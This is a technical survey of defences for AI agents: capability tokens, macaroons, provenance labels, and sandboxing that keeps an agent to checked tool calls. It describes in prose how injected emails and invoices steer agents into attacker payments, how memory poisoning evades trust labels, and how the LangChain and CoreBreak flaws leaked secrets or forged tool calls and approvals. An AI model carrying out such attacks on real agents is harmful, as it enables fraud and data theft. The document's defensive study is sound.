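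To store a reference or send it by email, a program needs a form of it that outlasts the connection, called a sturdy reference. In the OCaml package *capnp-rpc-lwt*, a sturdy reference has three parts: the host's network address, a way to authenticate the host, and a secret that identifies the object and proves permission to use it. The secret is often called a "Swiss number", after bank accounts that supposedly opened to anyone who knew the number. The manual for Goblins, a programming system from the Spritely Institute, shows a sturdy reference as a web-style address ending in 43 random-looking characters. These are enough to hold 256 random bits, so nobody could realistically guess the address.

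Anyone who learns an object's Swiss number can use the object. Any channel that carries data can therefore also carry access, and a process can gain access to an object without a connection that passes capabilities. For example, Cassie's one-way channel accepted only integers so that Q could not send Bond a capability. But a Swiss number is an integer, so if Q has one and Bond can reach the object's host, Q can send the number through the channel and Bond can use the object.

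Spritely Institute's *The Heart of Spritely* describes certificates as harder to share than such addresses but less likely to leak. The paper also describes how Goblins saves a running program without letting objects gain authority. Each object provides a description of itself for storage, which can use only permissions the object already has. In a multiplayer game, an object that a player built could not gain the power to issue the game's currency by being saved and restored.

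### Macaroons: tokens that carry their own limits

The host of a Swiss number must record what the number grants. In the mailing-list thread *Comparing capability systems* (2026), Karp compared such numbers with encrypted certificates and found that they differ significantly only in where this information is kept. A macaroon keeps its limits in readable form in the token itself, so that a holder can add more limits. Birgisson, Politz and colleagues designed these tokens for cloud services in *Macaroons* (2014).

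A macaroon relies on a keyed hash called an HMAC. It turns a key and a message into a short value that nobody can compute without the key, and the value does not reveal the key. In the paper's example, a storage service keeps data in numbered chunks. It has a secret key K and creates a token with a random identifier N. Two restrictions, called caveats, then narrow the token:

s₀ = HMAC(K, N) = 90..fc

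s₁ = HMAC(s₀, "chunk ∈ {100..500}") = f5..30

s₂ = HMAC(s₁, "operation == read") = 0a..9f

Each line uses the previous result as its key. A token with N and s₀ gives access to every chunk. The final token contains N, s₂ and the text of both caveats, but not s₀ or s₁.

When a request arrives, the service starts from K, recomputes the chain from the text in the token, and checks that the result equals s₂. It then tests every caveat against the request. A request to read chunk 235 succeeds, while requests to write to chunk 235 or read chunk 600 fail.

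The holder can add a time limit without contacting the service by computing s₃ = HMAC(s₂, "time < 3 pm") and replacing s₂ with s₃. Removing the "read" caveat would require s₁, the value for a token with only the chunk caveat. The holder cannot recover s₁ from s₂, because s₁ was the HMAC key used to compute s₂, and cannot compute s₁ from the beginning without K or s₀. If the holder deleted the caveat's text, the service would compute s₁ and find that it did not match the token's s₂. Adding "operation ∈ {read, write}" would not restore write access, because every caveat must hold. The holder can therefore narrow the token's rights but not broaden them, although anyone who kept an earlier copy still has the broader rights.

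A macaroon can solve the queue problem in the support example. The mail program holds one that allows refund requests on any order. For each email, it adds the sender's order number and an expiry time, then gives the new token to the harness. The token is text, so the harness can put it in the queue record, and the dispatcher can check it hours later. The dispatcher still needs its $200 total limit per order, because the same token can be used more than once before it expires.

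A caveat can also require proof from another service. Suppose the company pays for a missing parcel only if the carrier has no record of delivery. The mail program creates a new secret key and puts two encrypted copies of it in a caveat, one for the carrier and one for the dispatcher. The carrier's copy comes with the claim the carrier should check. If the claim is true, the carrier uses the key to make a second macaroon, and the dispatcher pays only if it receives both macaroons. The mail program has to know the carrier, but the dispatcher does not.

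Birgisson and colleagues acknowledge that only the issuer can check an ordinary macaroon, because checking requires K, and anyone with K could also rewrite the caveats. They outline a public-key version that avoids this. They claim advantages over earlier certificate systems only in efficiency and ease of adoption. A macaroon is still a bearer credential, so it works for whoever presents it, but a caveat can restrict its use, for instance by naming the network address that requests must come from.

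### Tokens in a model's context

A language model can copy anything in its context into any output, whereas an ordinary program sends a token only where its code directs. If the harness puts a token in the prompt so that the model can include it in a tool call, injected text may lead the model to put it in an email or a web address as well. Lan, Kaul and colleagues got an agent to leak data from its context in this way, and a token in the context could leak the same way.

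One defence is to tie the token to a particular program. *Delegation Without Trust*, whose authors work for a company that sells a related product, tests a broker that does this. Each agent proves its identity cryptographically, and the broker issues it a token that works only with that identity. *Delegation Without Trust* reports that the broker accepted none of 200,000 forged or altered tokens. A stolen token worked only when the attacker could also present the victim's identity.

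Across 2,000 simulated cases, a compromised sub-agent could carry out an average of 1.5 actions with the broker, compared with all 8,100 when agents shared one broad token. The average is low mostly because the simulated tasks were narrow. The approach is also limited because a hijacked agent can still misuse its own token for any action the token allows.

Another defence is to keep the token out of the model's context. The harness stores it in a table and shows the model a short name, or handle, such as `refund_1`. When the model uses the handle in a tool call, a trusted program looks up the token and attaches it. If the model copies `refund_1` into an email, the reader gains no authority, just as a process that receives the text "5" gains no access to the sender's file descriptor 5. FIDES uses a similar method to hide untrusted emails from its planner.

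The program that resolves handles must replace a handle with its token only in the field where a tool expects a token. If it replaced the handle everywhere, an email that mentioned `refund_1` would go out with the real token inside. Each conversation also needs its own table, so that injected text cannot lead the model to choose a token meant for another customer's order.

| What an outsider copies | Can the outsider use it? |
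|---|---|
| File descriptor number | No, the kernel looks it up in the outsider's own table |
| Position in a connection's table | No, it has meaning only on that connection |
| Handoff certificate | No, it names the recipient's key |
| Swiss number | Yes |
| Macaroon | Yes, unless a caveat rules it out |
| Token tied to a program's identity | Only with that program's identity |
| Handle | No, unless the outsider can steer the agent whose harness resolves it |

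### Recording who acts for whom

Many agents reach other services through OAuth, a standard for letting one program act on a user's behalf without the user's password. OAuth token exchange extends this to chains of programs. A program presents the token it holds and receives a new one for the next service. The new token can record who is acting for whom, for example that a finance agent is acting for an orchestrating agent, which is acting for a user.

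*Delegation Without Trust* rates token exchange as fully supporting this record, but only partly ensuring that each new token grants less than the last, and not tying the token to its holder. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* adds that a typical OAuth permission, such as `files.read`, does not specify the task's purpose, which documents it involves or who may receive the results. An extension called Rich Authorization Requests can add details about a particular transaction, but someone still has to translate the user's request into those details.

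An accurate log can leave out what caused an action. In an example from the Spritely Institute, Lauren runs a news blog and gives Robert access that she can revoke and that logs everything done with it. Before going on vacation, Robert sets up a way for a teacher to approve a student's article, which is then published through Robert's access. When the teacher approves it, Lauren's log lists Robert as the publisher. The result is harmless here, and Lauren wants to hold Robert responsible for whatever happens through his access. But an agent's log would look the same whether or not injected text had caused the action.

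*Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* describes an orchestrating agent that was only supposed to summarize invoices, but an email led it to request a payment through a finance agent. The payment service had no way to detect that the email had caused the request.

If the agents had used token exchange, the final token could have accurately listed the user, the orchestrating agent and the finance agent. It would still have omitted the email, because the email never held or passed on any authority. The paper therefore distinguishes a graph of who delegated authority to whom from a graph of where content came from and where it can flow. A sound decision about the payment needs both graphs. The inbox belongs in both, as something the agent may read and as a source of text that may be hostile.

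A macaroon restricted to reading invoices would also have stopped the payment if it had been the only credential the finance agent could use. But the agent probably has its own payment credential for other jobs, and the payment tool would accept that one.

### Linking each action to the original request

In *Proof-of-Continuity*, Gallo argues that any system that checks only possession of a credential has this weakness. The argument describes an action as (o, r, ℓ), where o is the operation, r is the resource and ℓ is the lineage, the chain of steps that led to the action. A policy A based only on possession ignores the lineage:

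A(o, r, ℓ) = A(o, r, ℓ′) for all ℓ and ℓ′

A payment that the user requested and one that an email prompted can have the same o and r, in which case the policy must allow both or refuse both. This follows from the definition, so it is mainly useful for sorting mechanisms. To distinguish the two payments, a check must use some information about their lineage, such as a one-time number tied to the request. Checking who presents the credential is not enough, because the finance agent is its rightful holder in both cases.

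Gallo concludes that a system can't have all three of these properties:

- Authorization decisions ignore lineage.
- Programs may hold authority of their own besides what arrives with a request.
- No request can lead a later program to use authority that did not come from that request.

Gallo gives up the first, because in practice services need their own authority. Supporters of capabilities could answer that a capability passed with a request is already linked to that request. Gallo accepts this for a single step, but the link is lost when a program stores the capability and later uses it for a different request.

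The proposed remedy starts each chain with a set C₀ of the actions the requester is entitled to cause. Each later step must prove that it follows from the one before, and its set of permitted actions can only shrink:

Cₙ ⊆ … ⊆ C₁ ⊆ C₀

In the invoice example, C₀ contains only the capabilities to read the inbox and summarize invoices, so no later step can make a payment as part of this request, even though the finance agent has a payment credential. The next program doesn't have to be running when the previous one finishes, so the method could in principle work with a queue.

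The model covers only single chains, not steps that combine several requests, and it does not specify how to construct the proof that links two steps. Programs also describe actions in different terms. The support agent requests a refund on an order, while the dispatcher transfers money, so someone has to define which transfers each request permits. If that definition is too broad, the chain will allow payments it should not.

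The most serious difficulty is that a hijacked program could falsely report that it initiated an action itself. The finance agent could report the payment as routine work, which would start a new chain with the agent's full authority. Gallo leaves it to the enforcement system to detect this, but that requires distinguishing the agent's own actions from those an attacker caused, which the payment service in the original example could not do.

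### A genuine request with altered content

Now suppose the user asks the agent to pay the invoices in the inbox rather than summarize them, and an attacker has replaced the account number on one invoice. Even if the continuity checks work perfectly, the payment goes through:

1. The user's request sets C₀, which allows payments from the company's account.
2. The agent reads the invoice as part of this task and passes the payment on with the same authority, so C₁ = C₀.
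3. The payment service receives a request to pay `acct_ATTACKER_999`. The request follows from the previous step, and C₁ allows payments from the company's account.

Every link in the chain is genuine, and no step gains authority. The lineage shows that the user's request led to the payment, but not that an attacker supplied the account number.

The user could prevent this by limiting C₀ to payments to the supplier's account. That works when the user or the company already has the correct account number. If the number appears only on the invoice, the user has to let the invoice determine where the money goes.

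A false refund claim also passes, because the customer really did send the request and it concerns their own order. The mail program therefore issues the right macaroon, and the dispatcher can trace the payment back to the customer's email.

Gallo distinguishes continuity, which follows authority through a chain of steps, from information-flow control, which follows data. To catch the altered invoice, the payment service would need a provenance label on the account number as well as proof that the payment continues the user's request. That label would have to reach the service's process along with the number.

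## Keeping provenance labels on data that is serialized and stored

An interpreter that tracks provenance keeps each label in its own memory, next to the value. When the agent writes a value to a queue, file or database, a later reader gets only the stored bytes. The writer therefore has to store the label with the value, and the reader needs a reason to trust the label.

Suppose one program writes a value with label l, and another reads it back with label l′. The label has survived if three things are true:

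- Restriction: l ⊑ l′, so the new label is at least as restrictive as the old one. An untrusted value must not come back as trusted.
- Binding: l′ belongs to this exact value in this exact record. Nobody has changed the value underneath the label or moved the label from another record.
- Enforcement: the reader checks l′ before it acts on the value.

Each part can fail while the other two hold. Suppose `acct_ATTACKER_999` has the label {U}, for untrusted, and the agent stores it in a table that has no column for labels. If the payment service treats unlabeled values as trusted, it reads the account number back with the label ∅. Restriction has failed, although nobody tampered with the record and the service checks every label.

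Suppose the table has a label column, and another record holds a supplier's real account number with the label ∅. An attacker who can edit the table overwrites the number. The stored label is unchanged but now describes a different value, so binding has failed. A signature over both the value and the label would reveal the change. It must also cover the record's identifier, or the attacker could copy an old signed record over a new one.

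Even if the label {U} arrives intact, enforcement fails if the payment program reads only the account and the amount. The writer cannot prevent this, because the check belongs in the reader's code.

### Plain data that came back as an object

LangChain, one of the toolkits that Mellafe Zuvic audited, has to convert its own objects, such as messages and prompt templates, into a form it can store. The functions `dumps()` and `dumpd()` write an object as a set of named fields, and `load()` and `loads()` rebuild it. A field with the reserved name `lc` marks the data as one of LangChain's own objects. This field is in effect a one-bit provenance label, because `load()` builds an object if the field is present and otherwise leaves the data as plain data.

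Plain data can also contain a field named `lc`. LangChain's writing functions should have escaped such data, which means wrapping it so that the reading code can't mistake the field for a real mark, but they did not. As a result, data that an attacker had shaped like an internal object was loaded as one, according to OSV's *PYSEC-2026-373* (2026), an entry in a public database of software flaws. This was a failure of restriction, because the loaded data had a status that it did not have when LangChain wrote it.

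An attacker could exploit even an application that loaded only data it had written itself. Model responses carry extra fields, such as `additional_kwargs` and `response_metadata`, and prompt injection can influence what they contain. LangChain's own streaming and message-history features serialized those fields and later deserialized them.

One kind of LangChain object stands for a secret and names an environment variable, where programs often keep API keys. By default, `load()` replaced the object with that variable's value. The attacker supplied only a name, as Tymshare's customer had, and `load()` looked it up with the application's own rights. An attacker could also make `load()` create objects from a list of approved classes, with settings the attacker chose. Cyata (2025), the security company whose researcher found the flaw, reports that creating an object of one approved class sent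 a request to an address the attacker could choose. The request could carry the secret, so the attacker did not need to see any of the model's replies.

OSV's *CVE-2025-68664* (2025) lists two affected ranges of the core package: versions before 0.3.81, and versions from 1.0.0 up to but not including 1.2.5. Versions 0.3.81 and 1.2.5, released in December 2025, escape the reserved field. The maintainers also changed `load()` so that by default it accepts fewer classes, does not read secrets from the environment, and rejects Jinja2 templates, which can run code. These defaults limit the damage if an attacker finds another way to forge the mark.

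Within months, GitLab's *CVE-2026-44843* (2026) described another way for an attacker's data to bypass the escaping. It also described older parts of LangChain that still accepted every class the toolkit could serialize. Versions 0.3.85 and 1.3.3 fix both problems. Applications that first reduced each request to a plain string were unlikely to be at risk, because a string has no fields where an attacker could forge a mark.

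Cyata's researcher explains that the original bug survived for two and a half years partly because it consisted of missing code, and partly because it was in the serialization functions, while someone looking for this kind of flaw would usually examine the deserialization functions. When a format stores its labels among the data, the serializer has to escape all data that could be mistaken for a label, and missing a single case is enough to let an attacker forge one.

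### Tool calls that no model had made

In August 2026 Hedi Ingber and Aviyam Ivgi, co-founders of a company called Stealth, presented a group of flaws they named CoreBreak. The Hacker News (2026) reports that agent software from Amazon Web Services (AWS), Google and Vercel ran data formatted as a model's tool call without checking that a model had produced it. In several of the attacks the model never ran, so instructions in its prompt and filters on its replies had no effect.

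The AWS flaw was an enforcement failure. A caller with a valid login could put a tool call in the last message of a request to Amazon's Bedrock AgentCore service, and the harness ran the tool without invoking the model.

Google's Agent Development Kit (ADK) lets a developer require a person's approval before a sensitive tool runs. Someone who could insert events into the agent's session history could forge that approval, because ADK checked that an approval existed but not that it matched the tool and arguments in the original call. A separate flaw, in sessions that a user can pause and resume, meant that ADK could run a tool call the user had written.

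Vercel's software passes tool requests from a sandbox to the host machine. It accepted requests from any process whose command line contained the path of an approved helper script. Malicious code already running in the sandbox could meet that test by including the path in its own command line.

| Software | Identifier | Affected | Fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| Amazon Bedrock AgentCore | CVE-2026-18830 | Managed service before July 31, 2026 | AWS rejects tool calls written by callers |
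| Strands for Python, from AWS | None | Shortcut still present on August 5, 2026 | Warning in the documentation |
| Google ADK for Python, forged approvals | CVE-2026-18236 | Before 2.5.0 | 2.5.0 |
| Google ADK for Python, resumed sessions | None | Before 2.5.0, in a non-default mode | 2.5.0 |
| Vercel `@ai-sdk/harness-codex` | CVE-2026-64650 | Through 1.0.28 | 1.0.29 |
| Vercel `@ai-sdk/harness-opencode` | CVE-2026-64651 | Through 1.0.27 | 1.0.28 |

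According to the researchers, AgentCore's harness is built on the open-source framework Strands. If the latest message in a conversation contains a tool call, Strands by design skips the model and runs the tool. AWS holds customers responsible for keeping untrusted callers from writing to the conversation history. Customers can do this if their application builds the history itself, but its security then also depends on whatever database stores the history.

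Vercel's fix comes closest to binding. The host now accepts a request only if it matches a short-lived, one-time authorization for the exact tool and input that appeared in the model's output. But a harmful call prompted by injected text would still match its authorization. A label for the payment service therefore has to record both that the model wrote the request and what the model had read. The public records contain no information on whether anyone exploited these flaws before the vendors fixed them.

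### DStar: labels that cross between machines

DStar, a 2008 system, meets all three parts of the requirement for messages between machines. Zeldovich, Boyd-Wickizer and Mazières designed it for websites that run code their operators cannot fully trust (*Securing Distributed Systems with Information Flow Control*). Their example is a payroll site whose tax-form generator needs one employee's data but should not be able to send it to anyone else.

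A DStar label is a set of categories. A secrecy category restricts who may receive a message, and an integrity category restricts who may have sent it. Label L₁ may flow to label L₂ if L₁ contains every integrity category in L₂, and L₂ contains every secrecy category in L₁. A program that owns a category may ignore its restriction.

Suppose the company from the invoice example creates an integrity category v for account numbers from its verified supplier records. It gives its payment program the label {v}, so only messages labeled v can reach that program. An agent that has read a stranger's invoice runs without v in its label and does not own v, so it cannot send a message labeled v, whatever it writes.

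On each machine, a program called an exporter is the only one that sends or receives DStar messages over the network. A message travels like this:

1. The sending program hands the message and its label to the local exporter. The operating system checks that the program may send data with that label.
2. The exporter translates the label from the operating system's local categories into global names.
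3. It checks signed certificates that allow the receiving exporter to handle every secrecy category in the label, then encrypts the message and sends it.
4. The receiving exporter checks certificates that allow the sending exporter to vouch for every integrity category in the label.
5. It translates the label into its own machine's categories, and the operating system delivers the message only to a program whose label permits it.

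In DStar, the global name of a category includes the public key of the exporter that created it. Any machine can use that key to verify a certificate for the category, or a chain of certificates that leads back to the key. DStar therefore needs no central authority to manage names. Exporters also don't have to contact a third machine to check a certificate, which matters because even a query can leak information.

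The certificates limit trust in other machines to particular categories. The owner of a category must still trust each host that handles it to translate the labels correctly and to enforce them on local programs. A compromised host could disclose or mislabel data only in the categories it is trusted to handle.

How much software the category's owner has to trust depends on the operating system. HiStar and Flume, two research systems, enforce labels on the programs they run. HiStar's kernel also labels every object it stores, so a queue kept there would retain its labels on disk. Linux has no label enforcement that DStar can use, so the owner has to trust all the software on a Linux host. A company that ran its agent and its payment program on ordinary Linux servers would get authenticated labels between the machines, but little protection from a bad program on either one.

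DStar labels a whole process, so the agent's output lacks v whether the agent copies the invoice, paraphrases it or merely lets it affect a decision. The drawback is that everything else the agent sends also lacks v, including account numbers it copied correctly from the verified records.

### MemLineage: labels on an agent's memory

Many agents save notes in a long-term memory and retrieve them in later sessions. An attacker can exploit this with a web page that the agent reads and summarizes. The agent saves the summary as its own note, and weeks later it retrieves the note for an unrelated request and takes a harmful action. *Memlineage* (Ouyang and Hou, 2026) and *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and Tang, 2026) both report that FIDES drops its labels when a run ends, so by then nothing connects the note to the page. A signature on the note would not help, because the agent did write it.

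Each entry in MemLineage, Ouyang and Hou's system, contains a note's text, its writer, a trust level, a list of the earlier entries it drew on (its parents), and a weight from 0 to 1 for how much each parent influenced it. A single signature made with the writer's key covers the whole entry, which binds the label to the text. A log that only allows additions makes it possible to detect missing entries.

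Trust levels run from 0, for trusted, to 3, for external material such as web pages. A new entry c gets the worst level among the parents that influenced it strongly enough:

trust(c) = max { trust(p) : w(p, c) > τ }

Here p is a parent, w(p, c) is its weight, and τ is a threshold that the operator chooses. Suppose τ is 0.3 and a summary draws on a web page with weight 0.8 and the user's note with weight 0.4. Both weights are above τ, so both parents count and the summary gets level 3. If no parent has a weight above τ, the entry gets level 0.

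Ouyang and Hou prove that an untrusted label lasts through any number of rewrites, as long as every link in the chain has a weight above the threshold τ. When the agent retrieves an entry, MemLineage checks the entry's signature and attaches its trust level. Before a sensitive tool runs, a gate checks whether the important arguments came from untrusted memory. If they did, the gate can refuse the call, ask the user, or replace an attacker's value with one from a trusted source.

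The main evaluation used fixed scripts in place of a model. Without a defence, all three kinds of memory attack succeeded. Signatures alone stopped the one in which the attacker had no registered key, and MemLineage stopped all three. These results show that the defence's logic works as designed, but not how often the attacks would succeed against real models.

Smaller tests used live models. In one, the agent summarized an untrusted document in one session and recalled the summary in the next:

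| Model | Harmful calls without a defence | Harmful calls with MemLineage |
|---|---|---|
| gpt-5.3-codex | 25% of 20 trials | 0% (95% interval up to 16%) |
| gpt-5.4-mini | 20% of 10 trials | 0% (95% interval up to 28%) |

A third model, gpt-5.2, never attempted the harmful call, with or without the defence.

Ouyang and Hou also ran six combinations of task and attack from AgentDojo's banking suite. The standard attack succeeded in only one of the six without a defence, and in none with MemLineage. When they set up the agent to treat records in tool output as instructions, the attacks succeeded in all six without a defence and again in none with MemLineage. In that test, the agent completed two of the six tasks when the gate only refused bad calls, and four when the gate could substitute trusted values. The trusted values came from the benchmark's own answers, which stood in for sources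 such as a bank's invoice records. A real company would have to provide and label such sources itself.

The added delay is negligible. Writing an entry took about 0.2 milliseconds, and checking one took less than half that.

### A signed label can still be wrong

A signature on a label shows which key signed it and that nobody has changed it since, but the label may have been wrong when it was signed. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 71 works on tracing what agents do, treats how a system produces its provenance records and how it protects them from modification as separate attributes. It finds little reporting of the protection. MemLineage does protect its records from modification, but its labels can still be wrong.

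Ouyang and Hou demonstrated three ways for this to happen, each with τ or the list of parents as the weak point:

- Omission: the agent saves a note derived from an untrusted page without listing the page as a parent.
- Dilution: the note draws mostly on trusted entries, and the page gets a weight of 0.2, which is below a threshold of 0.3.
- Repeated rewriting: the first summary gets a weight of 0.9, and each further rewrite gets 0.7 times the weight before it. By the fifth step the weight is 0.9 × 0.7⁴ ≈ 0.22, again below 0.3.

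In all three cases the note got the label "trusted" with a valid signature, and the harmful action went ahead. The mistake also spreads, because any later note that draws on this one starts from a trusted parent. The proof still holds, since it covers only chains in which every weight is above the threshold.

Part of the problem is that MemLineage trusts an entry with no strong parent by default, much as the payment service trusted an unlabeled account number. Stricter settings stopped all three attacks. One refuses any sensitive action that relies on a note with no recorded parents, and the others count every positive weight or lower the threshold for text that has been summarized several times. The first setting can also block legitimate actions, because a reminder that the user wrote has no parents either. In the scripted tests, it would have blocked a legitimate request to send an email.

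### NeuroTaint: estimating influence through paraphrase

The weights are hard to get right because a model can pass on a text's meaning without repeating any of its words. Cai and colleagues built NeuroTaint to detect such influence. Like MemLineage, it stores source labels with an agent's memory and restores them in later sessions. After a run, it checks the log to determine whether an untrusted source influenced each sensitive tool call.

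The method starts with the checks that need the least computation. It searches the tool's arguments for a unique marker that it added to the source text, then for wording shared with the source. Next, it converts the source and the arguments into lists of numbers that represent their meaning and measures how similar they are. It repeats this comparison for small pieces of the source, since an injected sentence may be a tiny part of a long page.

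If none of this finds a link, NeuroTaint tests for implicit influence. It replaces the source with a neutral placeholder, such as a message saying the search found nothing, and asks a model whether the agent would still have made the same call. For example, an email announcing a new "policy" might lead an agent to forward a customer's message to an attacker. The forwarded message contains nothing from the policy email, but the agent would not have sent it without that email.

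Cai and colleagues tested NeuroTaint and FIDES on TaintBench, a set of 400 scenarios they wrote for 20 agent frameworks. An untrusted source influenced a sensitive call in half the scenarios.

| Result | NeuroTaint | FIDES |
|---|---|---|
| Influence detected, all cases | 187 of 200 | 108 of 200 |
| Influence detected, rewritten text | 75 of 85 | 40 of 85 |
| Influence detected, implicit | 37 of 40 | 17 of 40 |
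| False alarms | 16 of 200 | 106 of 200 |

The comparison favors NeuroTaint, whose designers wrote the benchmark. FIDES's false alarms are also partly due to its different purpose, since it is meant to block unsafe calls and so assumes influence wherever data could have flowed. The two systems scored almost the same on two existing benchmarks of unsafe agent behavior, which do not separate possible from actual influence.

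NeuroTaint's 13 misses matter more for security than its average score suggests, because ten of them involved text whose link to the source had weakened through paraphrase or storage, and an attacker could deliberately try to produce such cases. NeuroTaint also audits a run after it ends, so it can help a company find a bad payment but not stop it. The audit took an average of 0.25 seconds for each unit of execution, which might be fast enough for a live check, but Cai and colleagues did not test one.

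Ouyang and Hou point out that NeuroTaint does not sign its labels, so someone who can write to the memory store could change them. NeuroTaint's estimates could in principle supply the weights for MemLineage, but a wrong estimate would then get a valid signature.

### When almost everything becomes untrusted

A designer who doesn't want to rely on estimates of which inputs influenced an output can assume that they all did. Each summary then inherits the label of its least trusted source, so the untrusted share of the agent's memory grows quickly.

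Suppose 1 percent of the entries in an agent's memory come from outsiders. The agent writes a first generation of notes, each drawing on five entries picked at random. It then writes a second generation, each drawing on five notes from the first, and so on. A note in generation g depends on 5ᵍ original entries, and it stays trusted only if all of them were trusted. The untrusted share is therefore:

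1 − 0.99^(5ᵍ)

| Generation of notes | Share labeled untrusted |
|---|---|
| Original entries | 1.0% |
| 1 | 4.9% |
| 2 | 22.2% |
| 3 | 71.5% |
| 4 | 99.8% |

Real notes would overlap more and grow less regularly, but the untrusted label would still spread. By the fourth generation, a rule against payments based on untrusted notes would block nearly every payment that relied on memory. The labels would be correct, since an outsider could have influenced almost any note, but they would no longer help tell a suspicious payment from an ordinary one.

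One remedy is to pass on only the labels of inputs that had a real effect, as MemLineage's threshold is meant to do. Cai and colleagues mention an earlier method that does this for single model replies. If only one of the five sources counted each time, the untrusted share in the example would stay at 1 percent. But this relies again on estimates that an attacker can try to defeat, and a single wrong label can turn hostile text into a trusted note.

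In DStar, a small program that owned the category v could also endorse an account number by adding v to its label after comparing the number with the supplier's file. That program then becomes part of the trusted base, and any mistake it makes carries over to every value derived from that number. If a person does the checking instead, the company has to pay for their time, and someone who sees hundreds of similar requests may start to approve them without reading them.

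The company could also stop the agent from using stored memory. Ouyang and Hou tested a simplified version of this in their scripted harness. It blocked all three attacks but also failed all four harmless tasks, because each task needed something from memory.

A more selective remedy is to check where each argument of a tool call came from, instead of judging the whole context. Ouyang and Hou compared the two rules on 13 sensitive actions, such as bank transfers and emails, that mixed trusted and untrusted material. Refusing any action with untrusted text in its context allowed none of them, while checking each argument allowed nine to be completed and blocked the attacker's values in all 13. The per-argument rule accepted arguments from trusted sources and replaced the attacker's values where a trusted source had the right one. It refused the call when only untrusted text supplied a value.

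Restricting which sources may supply each argument of a sensitive tool doesn't slow the growth of labels, but it makes the growth less harmful. The agent's notes about an invoice can all be untrusted, and the payment can still go through if the account number comes from the supplier's file. However, someone must choose the allowed sources for every argument of every sensitive tool and keep those sources accurate.

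## Whether authority can be certified beyond the agent's interface

Controlling the arguments of each tool call protects the tools an agent calls directly. A company may want a broader certificate, meaning a justified claim that no attacker input to the agent can cause more than a stated amount of harm, even through programs the agent never calls. Such a certificate has to cover the agent's authority, so it also depends on software the agent's developers did not write.

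### An argument in five premises

The argument that such a certificate is possible has five premises:

1. Tracking inside the agent is sound. The labels on its output never omit a source that influenced it, and its code uses only the capabilities it holds.
2. Every effect the agent can cause passes through an interface that the tracking covers.
3. Labels and capabilities survive each crossing into another process or into storage.
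4. Each downstream program enforces them, or someone has proved a limit on what the program does.
5. Every endorsement is justified.

If all five premises are true, the conclusion follows step by step. Output leaves the agent only through known exits and with correct labels. It reaches the next program with those labels intact, and that program either refuses what they forbid or stays within its proved limit. The same reasoning applies to whatever that program sends on. The only exceptions are endorsements, which are justified. The dispute is therefore about whether all five premises can be true of a working system.

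Sound tracking inside the agent has the best support. LLMbda's theorem covers every program in its language, and TACIT's compiler rejects code that uses an undeclared capability. Both systems rely on compilers and operating systems outside their proofs, so a critic can object that these results describe a model of the agent rather than the machine it runs on. The best reply is that proofs can also cover machine code. Klein, Andronick and colleagues describe a proof that the binary code of the seL4 kernel correctly implements its C source in *Comprehensive Formal Verification of an OS Microkernel*.

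Showing that every effect passes through a tracked interface is harder, because an agent can affect other programs by routes that nobody designed as outputs. Cline's triage agent, for example, could reach the release workflow through a shared cache. Designers can respond by closing off all other routes instead of listing them. *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (Ciliberto, Rudi and Tassi, 2026) describes a system in which the agent must supply, with each tool call, a proof that the call follows agreed rules, such as a spending limit. A program called the Airlock checks the proof and only then runs the call. The agent and every process it starts run in a sandbox without access to the Airlock's files, memory or credentials. The sandbox's only network route, if the rules allow one, is to the model's provider.

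Ciliberto and colleagues prove that if an agent can act only through its requests, any effect a tool has while the agent runs could also occur without the agent, given the same input. An engineer can therefore analyze the tools once and reuse the result for every such agent, including hostile ones. An agent would violate the condition if it could influence a running tool through a shared file, or if it shared a cache with a release workflow.

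A label can also survive a crossing and still change its meaning, because two programs may describe actions in different terms. Gallo represents this with a translation T from the actions Cᵢ permitted at one step into the terms of the next step, and requires:

Cᵢ₊₁ ⊆ T(Cᵢ)

If the translation T turns a refund on order 1001 into "pay up to $200 to any account", a payment to the attacker satisfies the condition. Gallo takes T as given and leaves its verification out of scope. One reply is that a translation is small and changes rarely, so people can review it once for each pair of programs. A company can also avoid the problem if the next program is safe for every valid input, because that program then needs no label.

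A certificate needs only a limit on a downstream program's effects, not a proof that the program is correct. This matters because most downstream programs do not check labels, and few companies could prove much about an entire payment service. Ciliberto and colleagues show how to certify such a limit for payments. The Airlock keeps the account's credentials and records each payment instruction, with its recipient and maximum amount, in a protected register before sending it, because the provider may charge the account before any reply arrives. The entry stays in the register even if the request times out, since the provider may still act on it. If the provider accepts only authenticated instructions and respects each maximum, it cannot charge more than the sum of the maximum amounts in the register. Both conditions are assumptions about another company's software.

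Endorsements are the weakest point, because no proof can show that a decision based on a customer's word was right. Garby and colleagues observe that the attacks that remain in tests of CaMeL, FIDES, TACIT and their own agent are of the same few kinds. They consider this a general limit of information-flow defences.

The best reply is to certify a limit on the damage without certifying that the decision is right. In an example from Ciliberto and colleagues, an agent may book only hotels that a fixed model with a fixed prompt has rated at least 7 out of 10, and may commit at most €2,000. A hotel with fake reviews might still get a 7, but the agent could not commit more than €2,000.

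### What the seL4 proof covers

seL4 is a microkernel, an operating-system kernel that provides only basic services such as threads, memory and message passing. It controls access with capabilities. Sewell, Winwood and colleagues (2011), in *seL4 Enforces Integrity*, used a computer proof checker to establish two theorems about it:

- Integrity: a kernel call changes only what the policy allows the running component to change.
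- Authority confinement: a kernel call never takes the system's access rights beyond those in the policy.

An earlier proof had connected the kernel's specification to its C code, so the theorems apply to the code that runs. The new proof took about ten person-months and 10,500 lines. It revealed no violation of integrity in the kernel.

A running system can contain hundreds of thousands of capabilities. To keep the policy manageable, Sewell and colleagues group the system's objects into components and draw a graph with arrows between the components. Each arrow represents one of seven kinds of authority: Read, Write, Send, Receive, Reset (the power to interrupt a message channel), Grant (the right to send capabilities along with a message) and Everything, which covers all the rest.

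Their example is a device that connects a terminal to either of two networks without letting information pass between the networks. Its router is a complete copy of Linux, whose millions of lines of code are far too many to verify. The theorems still limit what the router can change, because the kernel and the policy set that limit, not the router's code. This is strong evidence that a company can limit the direct effects of a program it doesn't trust.

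The theorems apply only if the system's actual access rights match the policy at the start, and Sewell and colleagues left the proof of this for future work. The running component must also not have Everything authority over another component. If it can exchange capabilities with another component, the policy must treat the two as one. The policy must also let the running component send any message that an interrupt could deliver, since an interrupt may arrive at any time. Integrity covers writing but not reading. In *seL4* (2013), Murray, Matichuk and colleagues later proved information-flow security for the kernel's 8,830 lines of C.

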